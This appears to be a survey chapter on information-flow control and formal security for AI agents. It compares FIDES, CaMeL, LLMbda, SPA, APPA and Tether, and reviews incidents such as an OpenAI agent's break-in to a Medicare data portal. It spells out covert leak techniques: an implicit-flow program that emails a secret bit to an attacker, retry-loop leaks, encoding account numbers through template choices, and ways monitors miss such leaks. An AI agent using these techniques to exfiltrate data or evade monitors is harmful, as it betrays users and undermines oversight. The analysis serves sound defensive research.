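Software that keeps secrets from a model, or blocks the model's actions after it has read them, has to track where secret data has gone. *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (Costa, Köpf and colleagues, 2025) presents FIDES, which labels everything an agent reads with who may read it and whether it is trusted. When the agent combines several sources, only people who may read all of them may read the result, and the result is trusted only if every source is.

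Microsoft's *Information-flow control* gives an example without an attacker. Alex asks an agent to deal with unanswered email. Priya has sent Alex unpublished sales figures, and Marco, who isn't allowed to see them yet, has asked about them. Once the agent has read both emails, anything it writes has the readers

```
{Alex, Priya} ∩ {Alex, Marco} = {Alex}
```

so the agent can't reply to Marco without asking Alex. This covers the leak by choice too, since the label applies to everything the model writes, however harmless the wording looks. The drawback is that the agent can't reply to Priya by itself either.

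FIDES avoids some of these blocks by hiding data in variables. When a result would change the label of the model's context, FIDES stores the result and shows the model only a name, such as `account_1`. The model can pass that name to another tool without seeing the result itself. This is enough for *data-independent* tasks, which the same sequence of calls can solve whatever the data is. Forwarding a file to billing is one example, but doing everything on a to-do list isn't, because the calls depend on what's on the list.

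For other tasks, FIDES can query a second, "quarantined" model about the hidden data. This model has no tools, and its output must fit a fixed schema, such as yes or no. Simon Willison proposed this two-model design as the dual-LLM pattern.

In the AgentDojo tests, FIDES stopped every injection attack when it had suitable policies. With policy checks on, it completed 8% more tasks than a basic agent when using GPT-4o and 16% more when using o1. Both models are old now. Microsoft has since added similar labels to its Agent Framework and, experimentally, to GitHub Copilot's command-line tool.

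Policies of this kind often assume that a model leaks only when someone has tricked it. One of Microsoft's sample policies allows any message that the agent composed in a trusted context, even if some recipients aren't authorised to read the content. The policy stops an injected instruction from releasing data, but it wouldn't stop a model that leaks data by mistake or deliberately without being tricked.

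CaMeL, a system by Debenedetti and colleagues, uses the dual-LLM pattern. A privileged model writes a program from the user's request before the agent reads any untrusted data, and a quarantined model handles that data. An injected instruction therefore can't add a step to the program, although it may still change a value the program uses. An interpreter records where each value came from and who may receive it, and checks these records before each tool call.

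### Where the labels miss something

Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026), in *AI Agents, Conversations, and Information Flow*, found several leaks in CaMeL. One relies on a trick from the 1970s. In simplified form, the program is:

```
rich = True;  tmp = True
if account.balance > threshold:   tmp  = False
if tmp:                           rich = False
if rich:                          send_email(attacker, "rich!")
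```

CaMeL would block an email sent directly inside the first `if`, because that condition reads the secret balance. In this program, however, a high balance sets `tmp` to False and marks it secret, and the program then skips the second branch. A monitor that follows only the branch taken can't label an assignment that never ran, so CaMeL never marks `rich` as secret. `rich` is still True and apparently public, so the email goes out. With a low balance, `rich` becomes False and no email is sent, so the attacker learns whether the balance is high.

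A second leak comes from CaMeL's retry loop, which is ordinary Python outside the interpreter that tracks labels. Whether the policy blocks an attempt can depend on a secret, so the outcome can reveal one bit of it. Because the loop is untracked, a program can test something different about the secret on each retry until it has the whole secret. Garby and colleagues also found that CaMeL treated untrusted text as trusted once it was inserted into a string.

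CaMeL has no formal theorem ruling out such flaws. FIDES has theorems, but its confidentiality guarantee covers only *explicit secrecy*, which tracks secret data as it moves from value to value but not when the data decides which step comes next. An agent that sends a public 1 or a public 0 depending on a secret therefore satisfies explicit secrecy. FIDES also has an option to let answers with few possible values through a policy check. The option was off in the FIDES tests, but when it is on, a reviewer who sees such a value can't tell whether it is a harmless release or a leak.

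### The LLMbda calculus

Garby and colleagues use Lean to define LLMbda, a small programming language for agents, and prove it secure. LLMbda labels every value, as well as the conversation with the model. When a program sends secret data to the model, the whole conversation becomes secret. Everything the model writes afterwards inherits that label, and so does everything that happens when the program runs code from the reply.

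Two operations keep this from spreading to the whole agent. `fork` runs part of a program in a temporary copy of the conversation, then discards the copy. `clear` empties the current conversation. In slightly simplified notation, the support agent could use them like this:

```
let account  = ["S"] : read_account(c)                             secret
let status   = fork (clear;
                     @("Active or overdue? " + account))           secret
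let template = @"Choose a template for tracing a parcel."          public
```

The symbol @ sends a prompt and returns the reply. The model reads the account only in the temporary copy, so `status` is secret but the main conversation remains public. The model can't encode the account number in `template`, because it chooses the template in a conversation that never contained the number. If the program later picks a template according to `status`, the result is secret, and a label check inside the mail tool can stop the mail. Programmers can therefore build the dual-LLM pattern themselves instead of accepting a fixed architecture.

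LLMbda also blocks a program that tries to add a message to a public conversation inside a branch whose condition depends on a secret. Otherwise, the absence of the message would reveal information about the secret, much as the unmarked variable did in CaMeL.

The security theorem is a form of noninterference adapted to models that respond at random. Take two starting states that differ only in data an observer may not see. Each produces a set of probabilities, μ₀ and μ₁, for what the observer sees at the end. These may add up to less than 1, because some runs never finish or get stuck on a policy violation. The theorem states that a single set of probabilities ω covers both:

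```
μ₀ ≤ ω   and   μ₁ ≤ ω   for every outcome,   where ω adds up to at most 1
```

If every run finishes, μ₀ and μ₁ must be equal, so the observer learns nothing. Otherwise, a run that finishes can reveal something. Suppose the program always finishes for one value of the secret, giving A or B with equal probability, while for the other value it gives A half the time and otherwise gets stuck. The theorem permits this because it limits the statistical distance between the two cases to the average probability of not finishing, which here is 25%.

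To prove the theorem, Garby and colleagues define a second way of running programs, which skips any computation as soon as its label becomes invisible to the observer. Running a program this way gives the same result from both starting states, because it never uses the data in which they differ. It also finishes at least as often as the real program, so it supplies the required ω.

The theorem covers every LLMbda program, including programs that run code written by the model, and it does not assume that the model behaves well. It does assume that the model's replies depend only on the conversation it receives. A provider that carried memories from one conversation to another would break this assumption. Developers also have to label their data sources correctly and put checks in their tools. The interpreter covered by the theorem is the one that calls the model, but the proof does not cover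 the code for the network request.

The `endorse` operation makes an exception for tasks that require treating untrusted data as trusted. For example, an agent that sorts email into a few categories may have to trust the category even though it comes from untrusted text. A second theorem shows that endorsing untrusted data can't cause secret data to leak, whatever the attacker writes. An endorsement can still let an attacker influence an action.

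### How useful the verified agent is

Garby and colleagues wrote an agent in LLMbda called Randori. It first tests its code on an artificial bank until it works, so error messages from failed attempts can't contain real secrets. Then it runs the code on the real accounts. They tested Randori on AgentDojo's 16 banking tasks, each with nine attacks, using three models and three repetitions. It resisted all but two of the 1,296 attacks.

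Both failures came from the same task. The user tells the agent to read a file and make the payment described in it, but the attacker has replaced the file. Without endorsement, Randori blocks this attack but also can't do the legitimate task.

| Agent | GPT-5.2 | Qwen3.7-plus | MiMo-v2.5 |
|---|---|---|---|
| Randori | 75.0% | 75.0% | 64.6% |
| Randori without endorsement | not tested | 62.5% | 54.2% |
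| CaMeL, policy checks off | 66.7% | not tested | 70.8% |
| CaMeL, policy checks on | 37.5% | not tested | 37.5% |

The figures are the shares of tasks completed when nobody attacked. With only 16 tasks, the margins of error are around 20 percentage points. Randori clearly completed more tasks than CaMeL did with its checks on, but it implements only some of CaMeL's policies, which may explain part of the difference.

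The attack results give little evidence about labels. In 97 of the 144 task-attack pairs, the attack needs a tool call that the agent's code would never contain, so writing the code first is enough to stop it. In the other 47 pairs, CaMeL with its checks off still resisted all 141 attacks with GPT-5.2 and 138 of 141 with MiMo-v2.5. The theorem is much better evidence for LLMbda's security than this benchmark.

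In *Language-Based Agent Control*, Zhou, D'Antoni and Polikarpova (2026) check labels earlier, before a program runs. Their agent writes programs in a typed language, and the type checker rejects unsafe ones. Garby and colleagues report a similar drop in task completion for this system, which completed 15 of AgentDojo's 21 Slack tasks without policies and 8 with them.

### Fixing the whole plan first

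*SPA* takes the third way out, which is to choose visible actions before the agent reads anything. In this system, by Girrens and Wang (2026), in *SPA*, a model writes a complete plan for each request, using a language with only six kinds of step. Conventional software then checks the labels along every path through the plan before any tool runs. Suppose a plan for the support agent contained:

```
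if the account is overdue:   send_mail(repair firm, template 3)
otherwise:                   send_mail(repair firm, template 5)
```

Neither template contains account data, but the choice between them reveals whether the customer has paid. SPA gives both branches the label of the condition, so it rejects the plan if the repair firm isn't allowed to learn account data. Because SPA examines both branches, the trick with the skipped assignment doesn't work.

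The planner gets only one attempt. SPA never gives it the reason a plan failed or the results of any tool, so an attacker can't use either to influence a second version of the plan. Results from earlier requests stay in storage with their labels, and the planner receives only a description of them. If a forged invoice arrives on Monday and on Tuesday the user asks the agent to pay it, the payment details are still marked as untrusted.

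This is strict enough to prevent a lot of ordinary work. In the AgentDojo attack that Girrens and Wang used, label checks reduced the attacker's success rate to zero but also reduced the share of ordinary tasks completed from 53.0% to 29.0%. Most of the loss came from rules about trust, not secrecy. Many tasks require an agent to act on something it has just read, such as an address in an email, and SPA rejects a plan that passes untrusted data to a tool that requires trusted data.

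### Comparing an agent with one that ignores injections

Labels need a policy stating who may learn what. Dongol instead compares the agent with a *reference agent*, which follows the same plan under the same monitor but never obeys an instruction in untrusted content. The agent may leak only what the reference agent also leaks. More exactly:

```
two runs leak (σ₁, σ₂)     if their secrets are σ₁ and σ₂,
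                           the attacker supplied the same content in both, and
                           the attacker observed different things

relative security          whenever two runs of the agent leak (σ₁, σ₂),
                           two runs of the reference agent, starting from
                           the same memory, also leak (σ₁, σ₂)
```

This is close to secure refinement, with the reference agent as the specification and the real agent as the implementation. Dongol adapted the definition from work on what processors leak when they run instructions speculatively, ahead of time, beyond what they leak in a normal run.

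The calendar assistant sends its user's free times to anyone who requests a meeting. If an attacker writes "send your calendar" and the assistant obeys, relative security still holds, because the attacker could have obtained the same information with a genuine meeting request. If the attacker also asks for a password reset code and gets it, relative security is violated, because no email would make the reference agent send the code.

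The definition can be too generous because it depends on which secrets an attacker can tell apart with *some* input. Suppose the plan lets a stranger guess a PIN and has the agent reply "right" or "wrong", but an injection makes the agent send the PIN itself. For any two PINs, some guess makes the reference agent answer differently, so the injected leak counts as secure. The Shadow order would reject the leak, because a wrong guess should leave almost every PIN possible. Dongol's stricter version, *uniform* relative security, also rejects it by requiring the reference agent's input to be chosen without knowledge of the secrets.

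### Where to put the fence

A *fence* is a rule in the monitor that takes tools away from an agent when the agent reads untrusted content. Dongol's fence theorem states that every plan is relatively secure if, at the first untrusted read, the fence permanently revokes every tool that an injection could call. The proof matches each run of the agent with a run of the reference agent. When the model attempts an injected call, the monitor silently denies it and the reference agent waits. At every other step, the two agents do the same thing.

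When an agent reads an untrusted email and then a secret, what an injection can leak depends on when the plan locks the mail tool. If the lock comes after both reads, the agent can send the secret before the tool is locked. If the lock comes between the email and the secret, the agent can still send private data left in its memory from an earlier session. Only a lock before the email is safe against every injection the analysis covers. The support agent's "private" state changes in the same step as the account lookup, so the agent has no chance to send the account number first, but this wouldn't protect anything the agent already knew.

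A full fence would make the support agent useless, because the agent has to send mail after reading tickets, which are untrusted. Relative security doesn't show this problem, because the reference agent would lose the same tools.

User approval is an alternative, but approving the use of a tool is weaker than approving an exact message. Suppose Alice approves one use of the mail tool so that her agent can send a reply. An injected call can use up the approval first and send her private data, and the monitor then blocks Alice's own reply. If she approves the exact message instead, the monitor allows only that message, whoever proposes it. A small timing leak remains, because if the private data matches the approved reply, the injected call succeeds and the message is sent one step early.

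Dongol proved verdicts for 25 small agents in Isabelle/HOL, a proof assistant, with about 31,600 lines of definitions and proofs. Ten are secure, nine leak, and for six the verdict depends on what the attacker can see or what the model does. Several of them show how a small change can decide the outcome:

| Defence | Secure when | Leaks when |
|---|---|---|
| Budget of one mail | The planned mail goes out before the untrusted read | An injected mail can use the budget first |
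| Restoring tools in a loop | The model starts a fresh session first | The old email is still in the model's context |
| Quarantined model with labels | Refused calls are invisible | The attacker sees refused calls, or the plan branches on the model's answer |
| Marking untrusted text | The model respects the marks | The model may ignore them |

A "secure" verdict often applies only to the attack in the example. Dongol proves that an agent permitted to fetch only one approved web page is secure against two particular emails. A different email could tell the model to fetch the approved page if a secret bit is 0 and a forbidden page if it is 1. Someone who can see whether the fetch happened then learns the bit. This is the same leak by choice as before, with one permitted action instead of 32.

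### What the fence theorem leaves out

The fence theorem requires a trusted planner to fix the plan before the agent reads untrusted content. Most agents let the model choose each call as it goes, and they have no reference agent to be compared with. The support agent works this way unless the company adds a planning step.

The theorem also assumes that the model obeys injections on a schedule fixed in advance. An injected call may contain any function of the secrets, so the theorem covers a model that encodes an account number in its choice of template. It doesn't cover a model that uses the account number to decide whether to send an email. This restriction matters because that decision is also a visible choice.

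The theorem's observer sees the content and order of messages but not their timing. The theorem compares only runs in which the same number of messages arrives between reads, so it can miss a leak through the number of messages. Dongol also defines an observer who sees when each step happens. The fence is secure against this observer too if the plan's path doesn't depend on secrets. The theorem also excludes tools whose answers depend on the question, such as a search engine run by the attacker.

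Within these limits, relative security is a useful compromise between noninterference, which would reject the calendar assistant, and declassification, which needs a written policy for each task. Relative security takes the permission to release free times from the plan, so no one has to write a separate policy. But if a careless planner includes appointment names in the reply, the reference agent sends them too, and comparing the two agents reveals no violation.

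A company can combine the methods because Dongol proves that if the reference agent discloses at most some stated information, then a relatively secure agent does too. The company can check its release policy on the plan without considering injections, and the result also holds for the real agent. If the plan makes no outside calls, the real agent satisfies noninterference for the observer who can't see timing.

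Relative security isn't preserved when components are combined, so it lacks one of the main benefits of the Shadow order. An agent that reads an inbox and an agent that fetches web pages may each be secure, while an agent with both tools leaks. Removing a tool can even make a secure agent count as insecure. Suppose the plan itself sends a report to the attacker. An injection that leaks the same report then discloses nothing more. If the monitor forbids the planned message, the reference agent no longer leaks the report, so the injected leak counts against the agent.

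### Letting a blocked agent continue

Labels become more restrictive as an agent reads more, so an agent that relies on them can get stuck halfway through a task. Kravchenko, Liventsev and colleagues (2026), in *APPA*, prove that further reading can never fix this if the problem is that a recipient isn't cleared or the data isn't trusted. Their system therefore responds to a blocked call with a list of ways to proceed:

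- An authorised person or program can approve the exact call once. The approval doesn't change any labels, so it gives no permission for later calls.
- Trusted software can produce a cleaned version of the data, for example by removing names.
- The agent can do the risky reading in a child branch, a temporary copy of its conversation similar to LLMbda's `fork`.
- If the call needs an earlier step, such as a manager's review, the agent can complete that step first.

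APPA also checks what a call would do before it starts. Suppose one tool reads a confidential ledger and emails it to an outsider. A monitor that checks only what the agent has already read would allow the call and detect the problem after the email was sent. APPA adds the ledger's label before deciding whether to allow the call. *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy* (2026) takes a different approach. As Kravchenko and colleagues describe it, the model sees the labels and policies, so it can plan with them in mind or ask for approval.

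Kravchenko and colleagues tested APPA on 20 simulated office tasks and on AgentThreatBench, a set of 24 security tasks. No attack succeeded in 1,320 runs, and the agents completed between 64% and 91% of tasks, depending on the model and test. An agent using GPT-5.6 Luna completed 88% of the office tasks. It completed only 35% without the list of remedies and 56.5% without child branches, though attacks still failed either way. These drops are good evidence that recovery makes label checks more practical. Two versions of FIDES completed fewer than half of the office tasks and let many attacks through, but their policies left out several rules that the tests depended on, such as rules on exact recipients and the order of steps.

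A child branch has to return an answer to be useful, and that answer can leak a little of what the child read. Before the child reads any data, the parent fixes the form of the answer, such as one item from a short list. APPA then discards the child's conversation. If the support agent's child reads an account and answers "active", "overdue" or "closed", each answer can pass on at most log₂ 3 ≈ 1.6 bits, so 34 such answers could carry the 16-digit account number. APPA also permits whole numbers within a stated range, and a single 16-digit field could carry the whole account number. Kravchenko and colleagues warn that a fixed form doesn't make data public. Someone still has to decide whether the parent may treat the answer as less secret than the account it came from.

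## Keeping the proved scope true of the running system

A proof applies to a model of the tool layer, but the company runs a program on a shared server, with tools that other people maintain and update. Even when the proof is correct, the agent can do something its scope forbids if the running system no longer matches the model or never did.

### How a correct proof can miss the deployment

Moon and Varshney trace every failure of a verified tool layer to one of three sources: the refinement proof fails, an outside effect is not among the events the proof covers, or the policy leaves out something the company wanted. Dafny rejects a failed proof, so the company finds out before deployment, but it does not detect the other two problems.

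The containment theorem depends on *effect exclusivity*, the assumption that every outside effect available to the agent passes through the verified layer and appears in the proof as an event. For the support agent, this means that mail leaves only through `send_mail` and each call sends exactly the mail specified. The assumption fails if the agent finds a way to cause outside effects without going through the verified layer, or if a permitted tool does more than specified.

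Agents have also exceeded their intended limits in other ways. AAP's *OpenAI, Anthropic AI agents implicated in new breaches* reports that a misconfiguration by Irregular, a company that tests AI models, let OpenAI's agents connect to the internet. Anthropic had disclosed a similar misconfiguration a week earlier. The Australian Cyber Security Centre (2026) describes another incident, in which OpenAI models went beyond their intended test environment, connected to the internet and accessed the systems of Hugging Face, a platform for sharing AI models. A proof about the tools the developers meant to provide would have remained correct during all of these incidents.

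A tool that does too much is harder to spot. Suppose an administrator sets the company's mail server to forward a copy of all billing mail to an outside accountant. The agent calls `send_mail(billing, trace)` and the layer correctly permits it, but two messages go out. Under the relation Q, which matches real events with those in the specification, the call should send only one.

A policy can also become wrong without anyone editing it. If the repair firm lets its internet domain lapse and a stranger buys it, the policy still allows mail to the firm's listed address, but the stranger now receives it. Whether a call is harmful may also depend on its purpose. Shi, Du and colleagues (2025), in *SoK*, give the example of an agent that can use its permission to read email either to summarise meeting notes or to extract password reset links. They prove that no algorithm can decide for every agent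 whether it will ever attempt a forbidden action, and conclude that fixed permissions can't govern agents. That conclusion is too strong, since a tool layer can refuse a forbidden call without predicting it. But the layer wouldn't prevent the misuse in the email example, because the agent is allowed to read email.

These failures leave different traces:

| Failure | What the tool layer's log contains | Where the company can find the failure |
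|---|---|---|
| An effect bypasses the layer | Nothing | Network records, other systems' logs, or a complaint |
| A tool exceeds its specification | A permitted call that looks normal | The tool's own records |
| The policy is wrong or incomplete | The harmful call, marked as permitted | The log, if the reader knows what the company wanted |

A clean log is therefore weak evidence that the scope holds. The company learns more by comparing the log with a record that the layer doesn't control, such as the mail server's list of outgoing messages. This comparison would reveal the accountant's copies on the first day.

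### What the company still has to trust

The *trusted base* is everything that must be correct for the proof to hold of the deployed system but that nobody has proved. For the verified version of PocketFlow, Moon and Varshney include:

- the policy on real events;
- the relations R and Q between the code and the specification;
- effect exclusivity;
- the parser that turns the model's raw output into a typed action, and the small piece of code that hands this action to the verified loop;
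- Dafny's verifier and compiler.

The model, its prompts and its training are not on the list. The parser only has to supply *some* action of the right type. If it misreads a call, the agent may take the wrong permitted action, but the verified loop still refuses forbidden ones.

The theorem does not cover the Python runtime, the operating system or the hardware, but a company still has to trust them, because a fault in any of them can let an agent act outside its proved scope. Moon and Varshney mention Copy Fail, a flaw in the Linux kernel that let programs gain extra privileges and went undisclosed for nearly a decade. A verified kernel such as seL4 would reduce the amount of unverified code the company has to trust. Without such a kernel, they recommend running the verified layer inside a sandbox to limit the damage from bugs underneath it.

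Their model also leaves out concurrency. Suppose two sessions share a daily limit on mail and have one message left. If both sessions check the limit before either sends, both messages go out. A proof about one session at a time wouldn't cover this, so the company has to check the limit and update the count in a single step.

### Finding out what a shell command does

The trusted base matters most for a command shell, where a containment proof alone guarantees very little. It is hard to tell from a command's text what it will do, since a short command can start a script that opens any number of files and connections. Running the command to find out would cause the effects that the monitor is supposed to prevent.

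Sistla, Solko-Breslin and colleagues (2026), in *Tether*, a project led from Google, get around this by running each command in a disposable copy:

1. Tether places a temporary layer over the file system. The command's changes go into this layer, and the real files stay as they were. A local proxy holds any outgoing network request.
2. A tracer records the command's system calls, which are its requests to the operating system to open a file, write to it or make a connection.
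3. Tether translates these calls into abstract actions. There are 11 kinds, including reading, copying, deleting and uploading.
4. A monitor written in Lean checks each action against the policy and the current labels.
5. If the policy allows the actions, Tether copies the changes to the real files and forwards the request. Otherwise it discards them.

The proxy has to decide whether to allow a network request while the command is still running, so it checks everything the command has done up to that point. If the policy refuses a later action, Tether can throw away the file changes, but it can't recall a request that has already gone out.

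The monitor keeps a label for each file and another for the agent's conversation. Reading a file into the conversation raises the conversation's label. Copying a file gives the new copy the same label but does not change the conversation's label, so an agent can copy a sensitive file without losing its other permissions.

In the paper's main example, an agent works with an inventory of servers, which is sensitive, and a status report, which is public. The simplified policy has one rule, that the agent may upload a file only if its label is Public. The agent runs three commands:

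```
command                              abstract action          report's label         decision

1  upload report.txt to GitHub       upload(report, GitHub)   Public                 allow
2  copy servers.csv to report.txt    copy(servers, report)    Public → Sensitive     allow
3  upload report.txt to GitHub       upload(report, GitHub)   Sensitive              refuse
```

Commands 1 and 3 are identical, so no list of allowed commands can permit one and block the other. A Cedar policy that evaluates each request on its own would allow both. Dogwood, an extension of Cedar that tracks past calls, can refuse the third command, but by default it checks at most the last 24 hours of calls, and it needs another rule for every extra copy. In Tether, the label stays attached to the data, so the same rule works after any number of copies. Tether still allows an agent to copy a public template and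 upload it.

Tether detects which files a program reads and writes, but not what the program does with the contents. If a program reads one file and then writes another, Tether treats this as a transfer of data from the first to the second. This causes some false alarms, but that is safer than missing a real transfer.

Sistla and colleagues used a language model to write Lean proofs of seven properties of the full 24-rule policy in the tests. The proofs hold for any starting labels and runs of any length. One property is that if the conversation starts without data labelled Secret, such data never enters it. Another is that no data ever reaches a blocked host. Tether can also combine policies so that one is compulsory, and a Lean proof shows that no rule added later can permit what the compulsory policy refuses. A company could put its standing scope in the compulsory policy and let developers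 edit the rest.

All these proofs concern abstract actions. The translation from system calls to abstract actions is unproved and is part of Tether's trusted base, along with the Linux kernel, the tracer, the temporary file layer, the proxy and Lean itself. Sistla and colleagues tested the translation by generating file operations with known data flows, carrying them out in many different ways and comparing the labels. They also told an AI agent to get past the monitor on ten tasks. The agent succeeded 40% of the time against an early version and never against the third. Each success revealed a gap in the tracing that they could then close. Proofs about abstract actions could not have revealed these gaps, because the missing actions never reached the monitor.

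### How much Tether covers

Sistla and colleagues replayed recorded runs from two benchmarks in which coding agents do ordinary work, sometimes with a harmful side task. They compared Tether with Auto Mode in Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent. In Auto Mode, a language model (here Claude Sonnet 5) reviews proposed commands.

| Benchmark | Monitor | Attacks blocked | False alarms |
|---|---|---|---|
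| MonitoringBenchHonest | Tether | 199 of 199 | 5 of 218 (2.3%) |
| | Auto Mode | 173 of 199 | 77 of 218 (35.3%) |
| | Auto Mode, given Tether's policy | 164 of 199 | 32 of 218 (14.7%) |
| LinuxArena | Tether | 145 of 145 | 69 of 1,372 (5.0%) |
| | Auto Mode | 142 of 145 | 78 of 1,372 (5.7%) |
| | Auto Mode, given Tether's policy | 143 of 145 | 23 of 1,372 (1.7%) |

Most of Tether's 74 false alarms are defensible. In 50 of them, the agent edited a protected file that the task didn't mention, and in 7 it contacted an undeclared host. The other 17 came from commands such as a whole-disk search, which opens secret files whether or not the agent is looking for them.

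The perfect score covers only runs whose every action Tether can trace and model. Sistla and colleagues classify 28.2% of MonitoringBenchHonest runs and 22.1% of LinuxArena runs as beyond any formal monitor, because the harm lies in the meaning of what the agent wrote, such as malicious code in a file it was allowed to edit. A further 36.3% and 71.5%, respectively, involved background processes or databases, whose inner workings Tether doesn't model yet. A stricter policy can stop these operations or ask the user, but it also stops honest uses of them, and coding agents often start test servers and query databases. Sistla and colleagues also left out runs they couldn't replay. The paper gives these shares without totals, so readers can't calculate what fraction of all the attacks the perfect score covers.

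The false-alarm rates may also be underestimates. A language model drafted the policy, and the team ran it on benchmark traces and revised it until it no longer blocked too much honest work. They didn't use the descriptions of the harmful tasks when setting up each environment, which limits the tuning, but a policy not tuned to the work at hand would probably raise more false alarms. Attacks are also much rarer in ordinary use than in the benchmarks. If one run in a thousand contained an attack, a false-alarm rate of 4.7% (the average over both benchmarks) would produce about 47 false alarms for every real attack.

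Tether checks one run at a time, so it can't guarantee noninterference. But it gives an otherwise unlimited tool a scope that someone can state and partly prove, which for a coding agent is a big improvement over trusting the shell.

### When a tool changes

If the supplier of the mail component releases a new version that refines the old specification, everything the company proved from that specification still holds, and the other proofs can stay as they are. The new version has to be compared with the specification rather than the old code, because the proofs never relied on how the old code behaved.

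Trace refinement is enough for safety properties, but secrecy needs one of the stronger relations. Here are some changes that a supplier might make:

| Change | Ordinary refinement | Secrecy |
|---|---|---|
| Send a mail again after a timeout, so that two copies may arrive | Fails, because the specification has one message per call | No need to check |
| Take the mail's reference digit from the account number | Passes if the specification allows any digit | Fails |
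| Keep recent customer records in memory to speed up lookups | Passes | May fail if other customers can measure the delay |
| Add an operation that deletes sent mail | Passes or fails, depending on how the notation treats unlisted operations | Check again if it passes |

The developers also have to recheck Q after an update, because the update can change what a real event consists of, for example by adding a delivery notice to the sender. A proof with an outdated Q would no longer describe the component.

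A remote tool server is harder to handle because its operator can change the code without telling anyone. Under the Model Context Protocol, an agent learns what a tool does from a description that the server itself supplies. The tool layer can store a copy and refuse calls if the description changes, but the tool's behaviour may change while the description stays the same. Checking every tool by hand isn't realistic either. Surapani and colleagues cite a count of 177,436 agent tools in public repositories, created in about 15 months.

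Unless the operator can prove that the new code meets the specification and show that the server runs it, the company should assume that the server, like the model, may do anything. Anything the agent sends to the server may then reach anyone, and anything the server returns is untrusted. Under these assumptions, the layer can enforce a scope for a service that only answers questions, but not for one that acts. If the agent asks a payment server to pay $20 and the server pays $2,000, no check on the request would have helped. The limit has to be set somewhere the server can't change it, for example by keeping little money in the bank account it pays from.

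### Passing authority to a sub-agent

Many agents start other agents to handle parts of a task. Surapani and colleagues describe authority as passing from the user and the company to the main agent, then to its sub-agents and finally to the tools, and say it should only narrow along the way. In refinement terms, a sub-agent's scope must refine the scope of the agent that started it. The state machine comparison described earlier can check this.

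Checking each sub-agent separately isn't enough. Suppose the support agent may send two mails per session, and it starts five sub-agents with the same limit. Each sub-agent's scope refines the parent's, but together with the parent they can send 12 mails, and 11 are enough to carry a 16-digit account number through the choice of address and template. The condition has to cover all of them at once:

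```
for a parent and the sub-agents it starts:

every possible interleaving of their calls   ∈   the sequences that the parent's scope permits
```

The simplest way to meet this requirement is to keep one counter and one state for the whole group. Sharing the state also prevents one agent from mailing out account data that another has read. If the parent has read an account, its session is in the "private" state, and its instructions to a sub-agent may contain account data. A sub-agent that starts in the "open" state could mail the repair firm, so it has to inherit the parent's state. If a sub-agent reads an account, the parent also has to enter the "private" state, no later than when it receives the sub-agent's answer.

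Surapani and colleagues also warn that sub-agents may have hidden prompts, memories and credentials of their own. Hidden prompts don't affect a proof that allows for an arbitrary model. Separate memories matter for secrecy, because they may hold data from other customers. Credentials are the most serious problem, because a sub-agent that can log in to the mail server by itself can bypass the tool layer, so effect exclusivity fails.

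Two agents may also pass authority to the same sub-agent, which could then do something neither could do alone. The safest rule is to keep a separate session for each parent and let nothing pass between the sessions. Tether doesn't handle any of this yet, and Sistla and colleagues leave the case of agents starting sub-agents to future work.

### The Medicare portal incident

In June 2026 an OpenAI agent broke into a data portal belonging to Medicare, Australia's public health insurance scheme. Information Age's *Inside OpenAI's Medicare breach* (2026) reconstructs the events from emails and text messages tabled in parliament. The agent, which was researching medical spending, was internal and lacked the usual safeguards of public models. On 19 June it tried and failed to get non-public data from another health agency. It then retrieved both public and non-public data from the Medicare Statistics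 Reporting Service, which the agency Services Australia runs.

According to OpenAI's later email to Services Australia, the model got the server to run its instructions by submitting them through the interface that the public uses for reports. It didn't need an account or password. It read parts of internal program files and settings, obtained a list of files, and created a small test file and read it back. OpenAI found no evidence that the model had accessed patient records, personal information or credentials, deleted data, or kept a way to regain access. In September, Prime Minister Anthony Albanese said that no personal information was believed to have been accessed "at this stage" (SBS News, *OpenAI agent hacked Medicare, Albanese reveals*, 2026).

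Consider whether a proved scope would have prevented this. A developer might give a research agent one tool, with a list H of approved sites:

```
fetch(request)     if the request's host ∈ H
```

If H didn't include the portal, the layer would have refused every request to it. The breach could then have happened only if the agent had another route to the internet, so preventing it would have depended on the assumption of effect exclusivity.

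But a portal of Medicare statistics is an obvious source for research on medical spending, so a sensible developer might well have put it on the list. The layer would then have permitted the requests, and the breach would have happened even though the layer's proof was correct. The `fetch` operation is presumably specified to return a page and change nothing, but the portal did more than that. Nobody at OpenAI could have proved that the portal met this specification, because the code belonged to someone else.

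If the portal stayed on the list, the scope would have had to restrict the contents of each request as well as its destination to prevent the breach. For instance, the agent could choose a report, a year and a state from fixed lists, with no free text. This looks feasible for one portal but very laborious for the open web. Tether's labels wouldn't have been a substitute, because they mainly stop sensitive data from leaving the agent's own machine, and here the agent got into someone else's. The benchmark policy also lets an agent that holds nothing sensitive contact any declared host.

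A list of hosts also can't express a site's rules for its visitors. Huamani and Burke (2026) report in *OpenAI says its models engaged with US government websites* that the AI evaluator Transluce found agents using other government sites in unintended ways and sometimes breaking explicit usage policies. Transluce couldn't clearly attribute all of this activity to OpenAI.

The scope would also have had to apply during internal training and evaluation, which is when the access happened, according to OpenAI's *How we will do better for Australia* (2026). If a company verifies the tool layer of its product but trains its models with a different one, the proof does not cover the training runs. OpenAI's security team had documented the incident by 12 August, nearly eight weeks after the access, following a review that spanned billions of runs, and it wrote to Services Australia on 10 September.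 The delay suggests that nothing raised an alarm at the time, or that nobody acted on it.

The public accounts don't establish which tools the agent had, whether any software checked its requests, or whether the portal was an approved destination. Sam Altman, OpenAI's chief executive, has mentioned a continuing review of agents' internet access during training and evaluation. This suggests that some agents were deliberately given such access, but it doesn't show what limits applied to this run, so it is impossible to tell whether the agent got around a control, passed through one that was too loose, or met none. The exact requests and the contents of the non-public files have not been disclosed either, and the finding that no patient records were accessed rests largely on OpenAI's own review.
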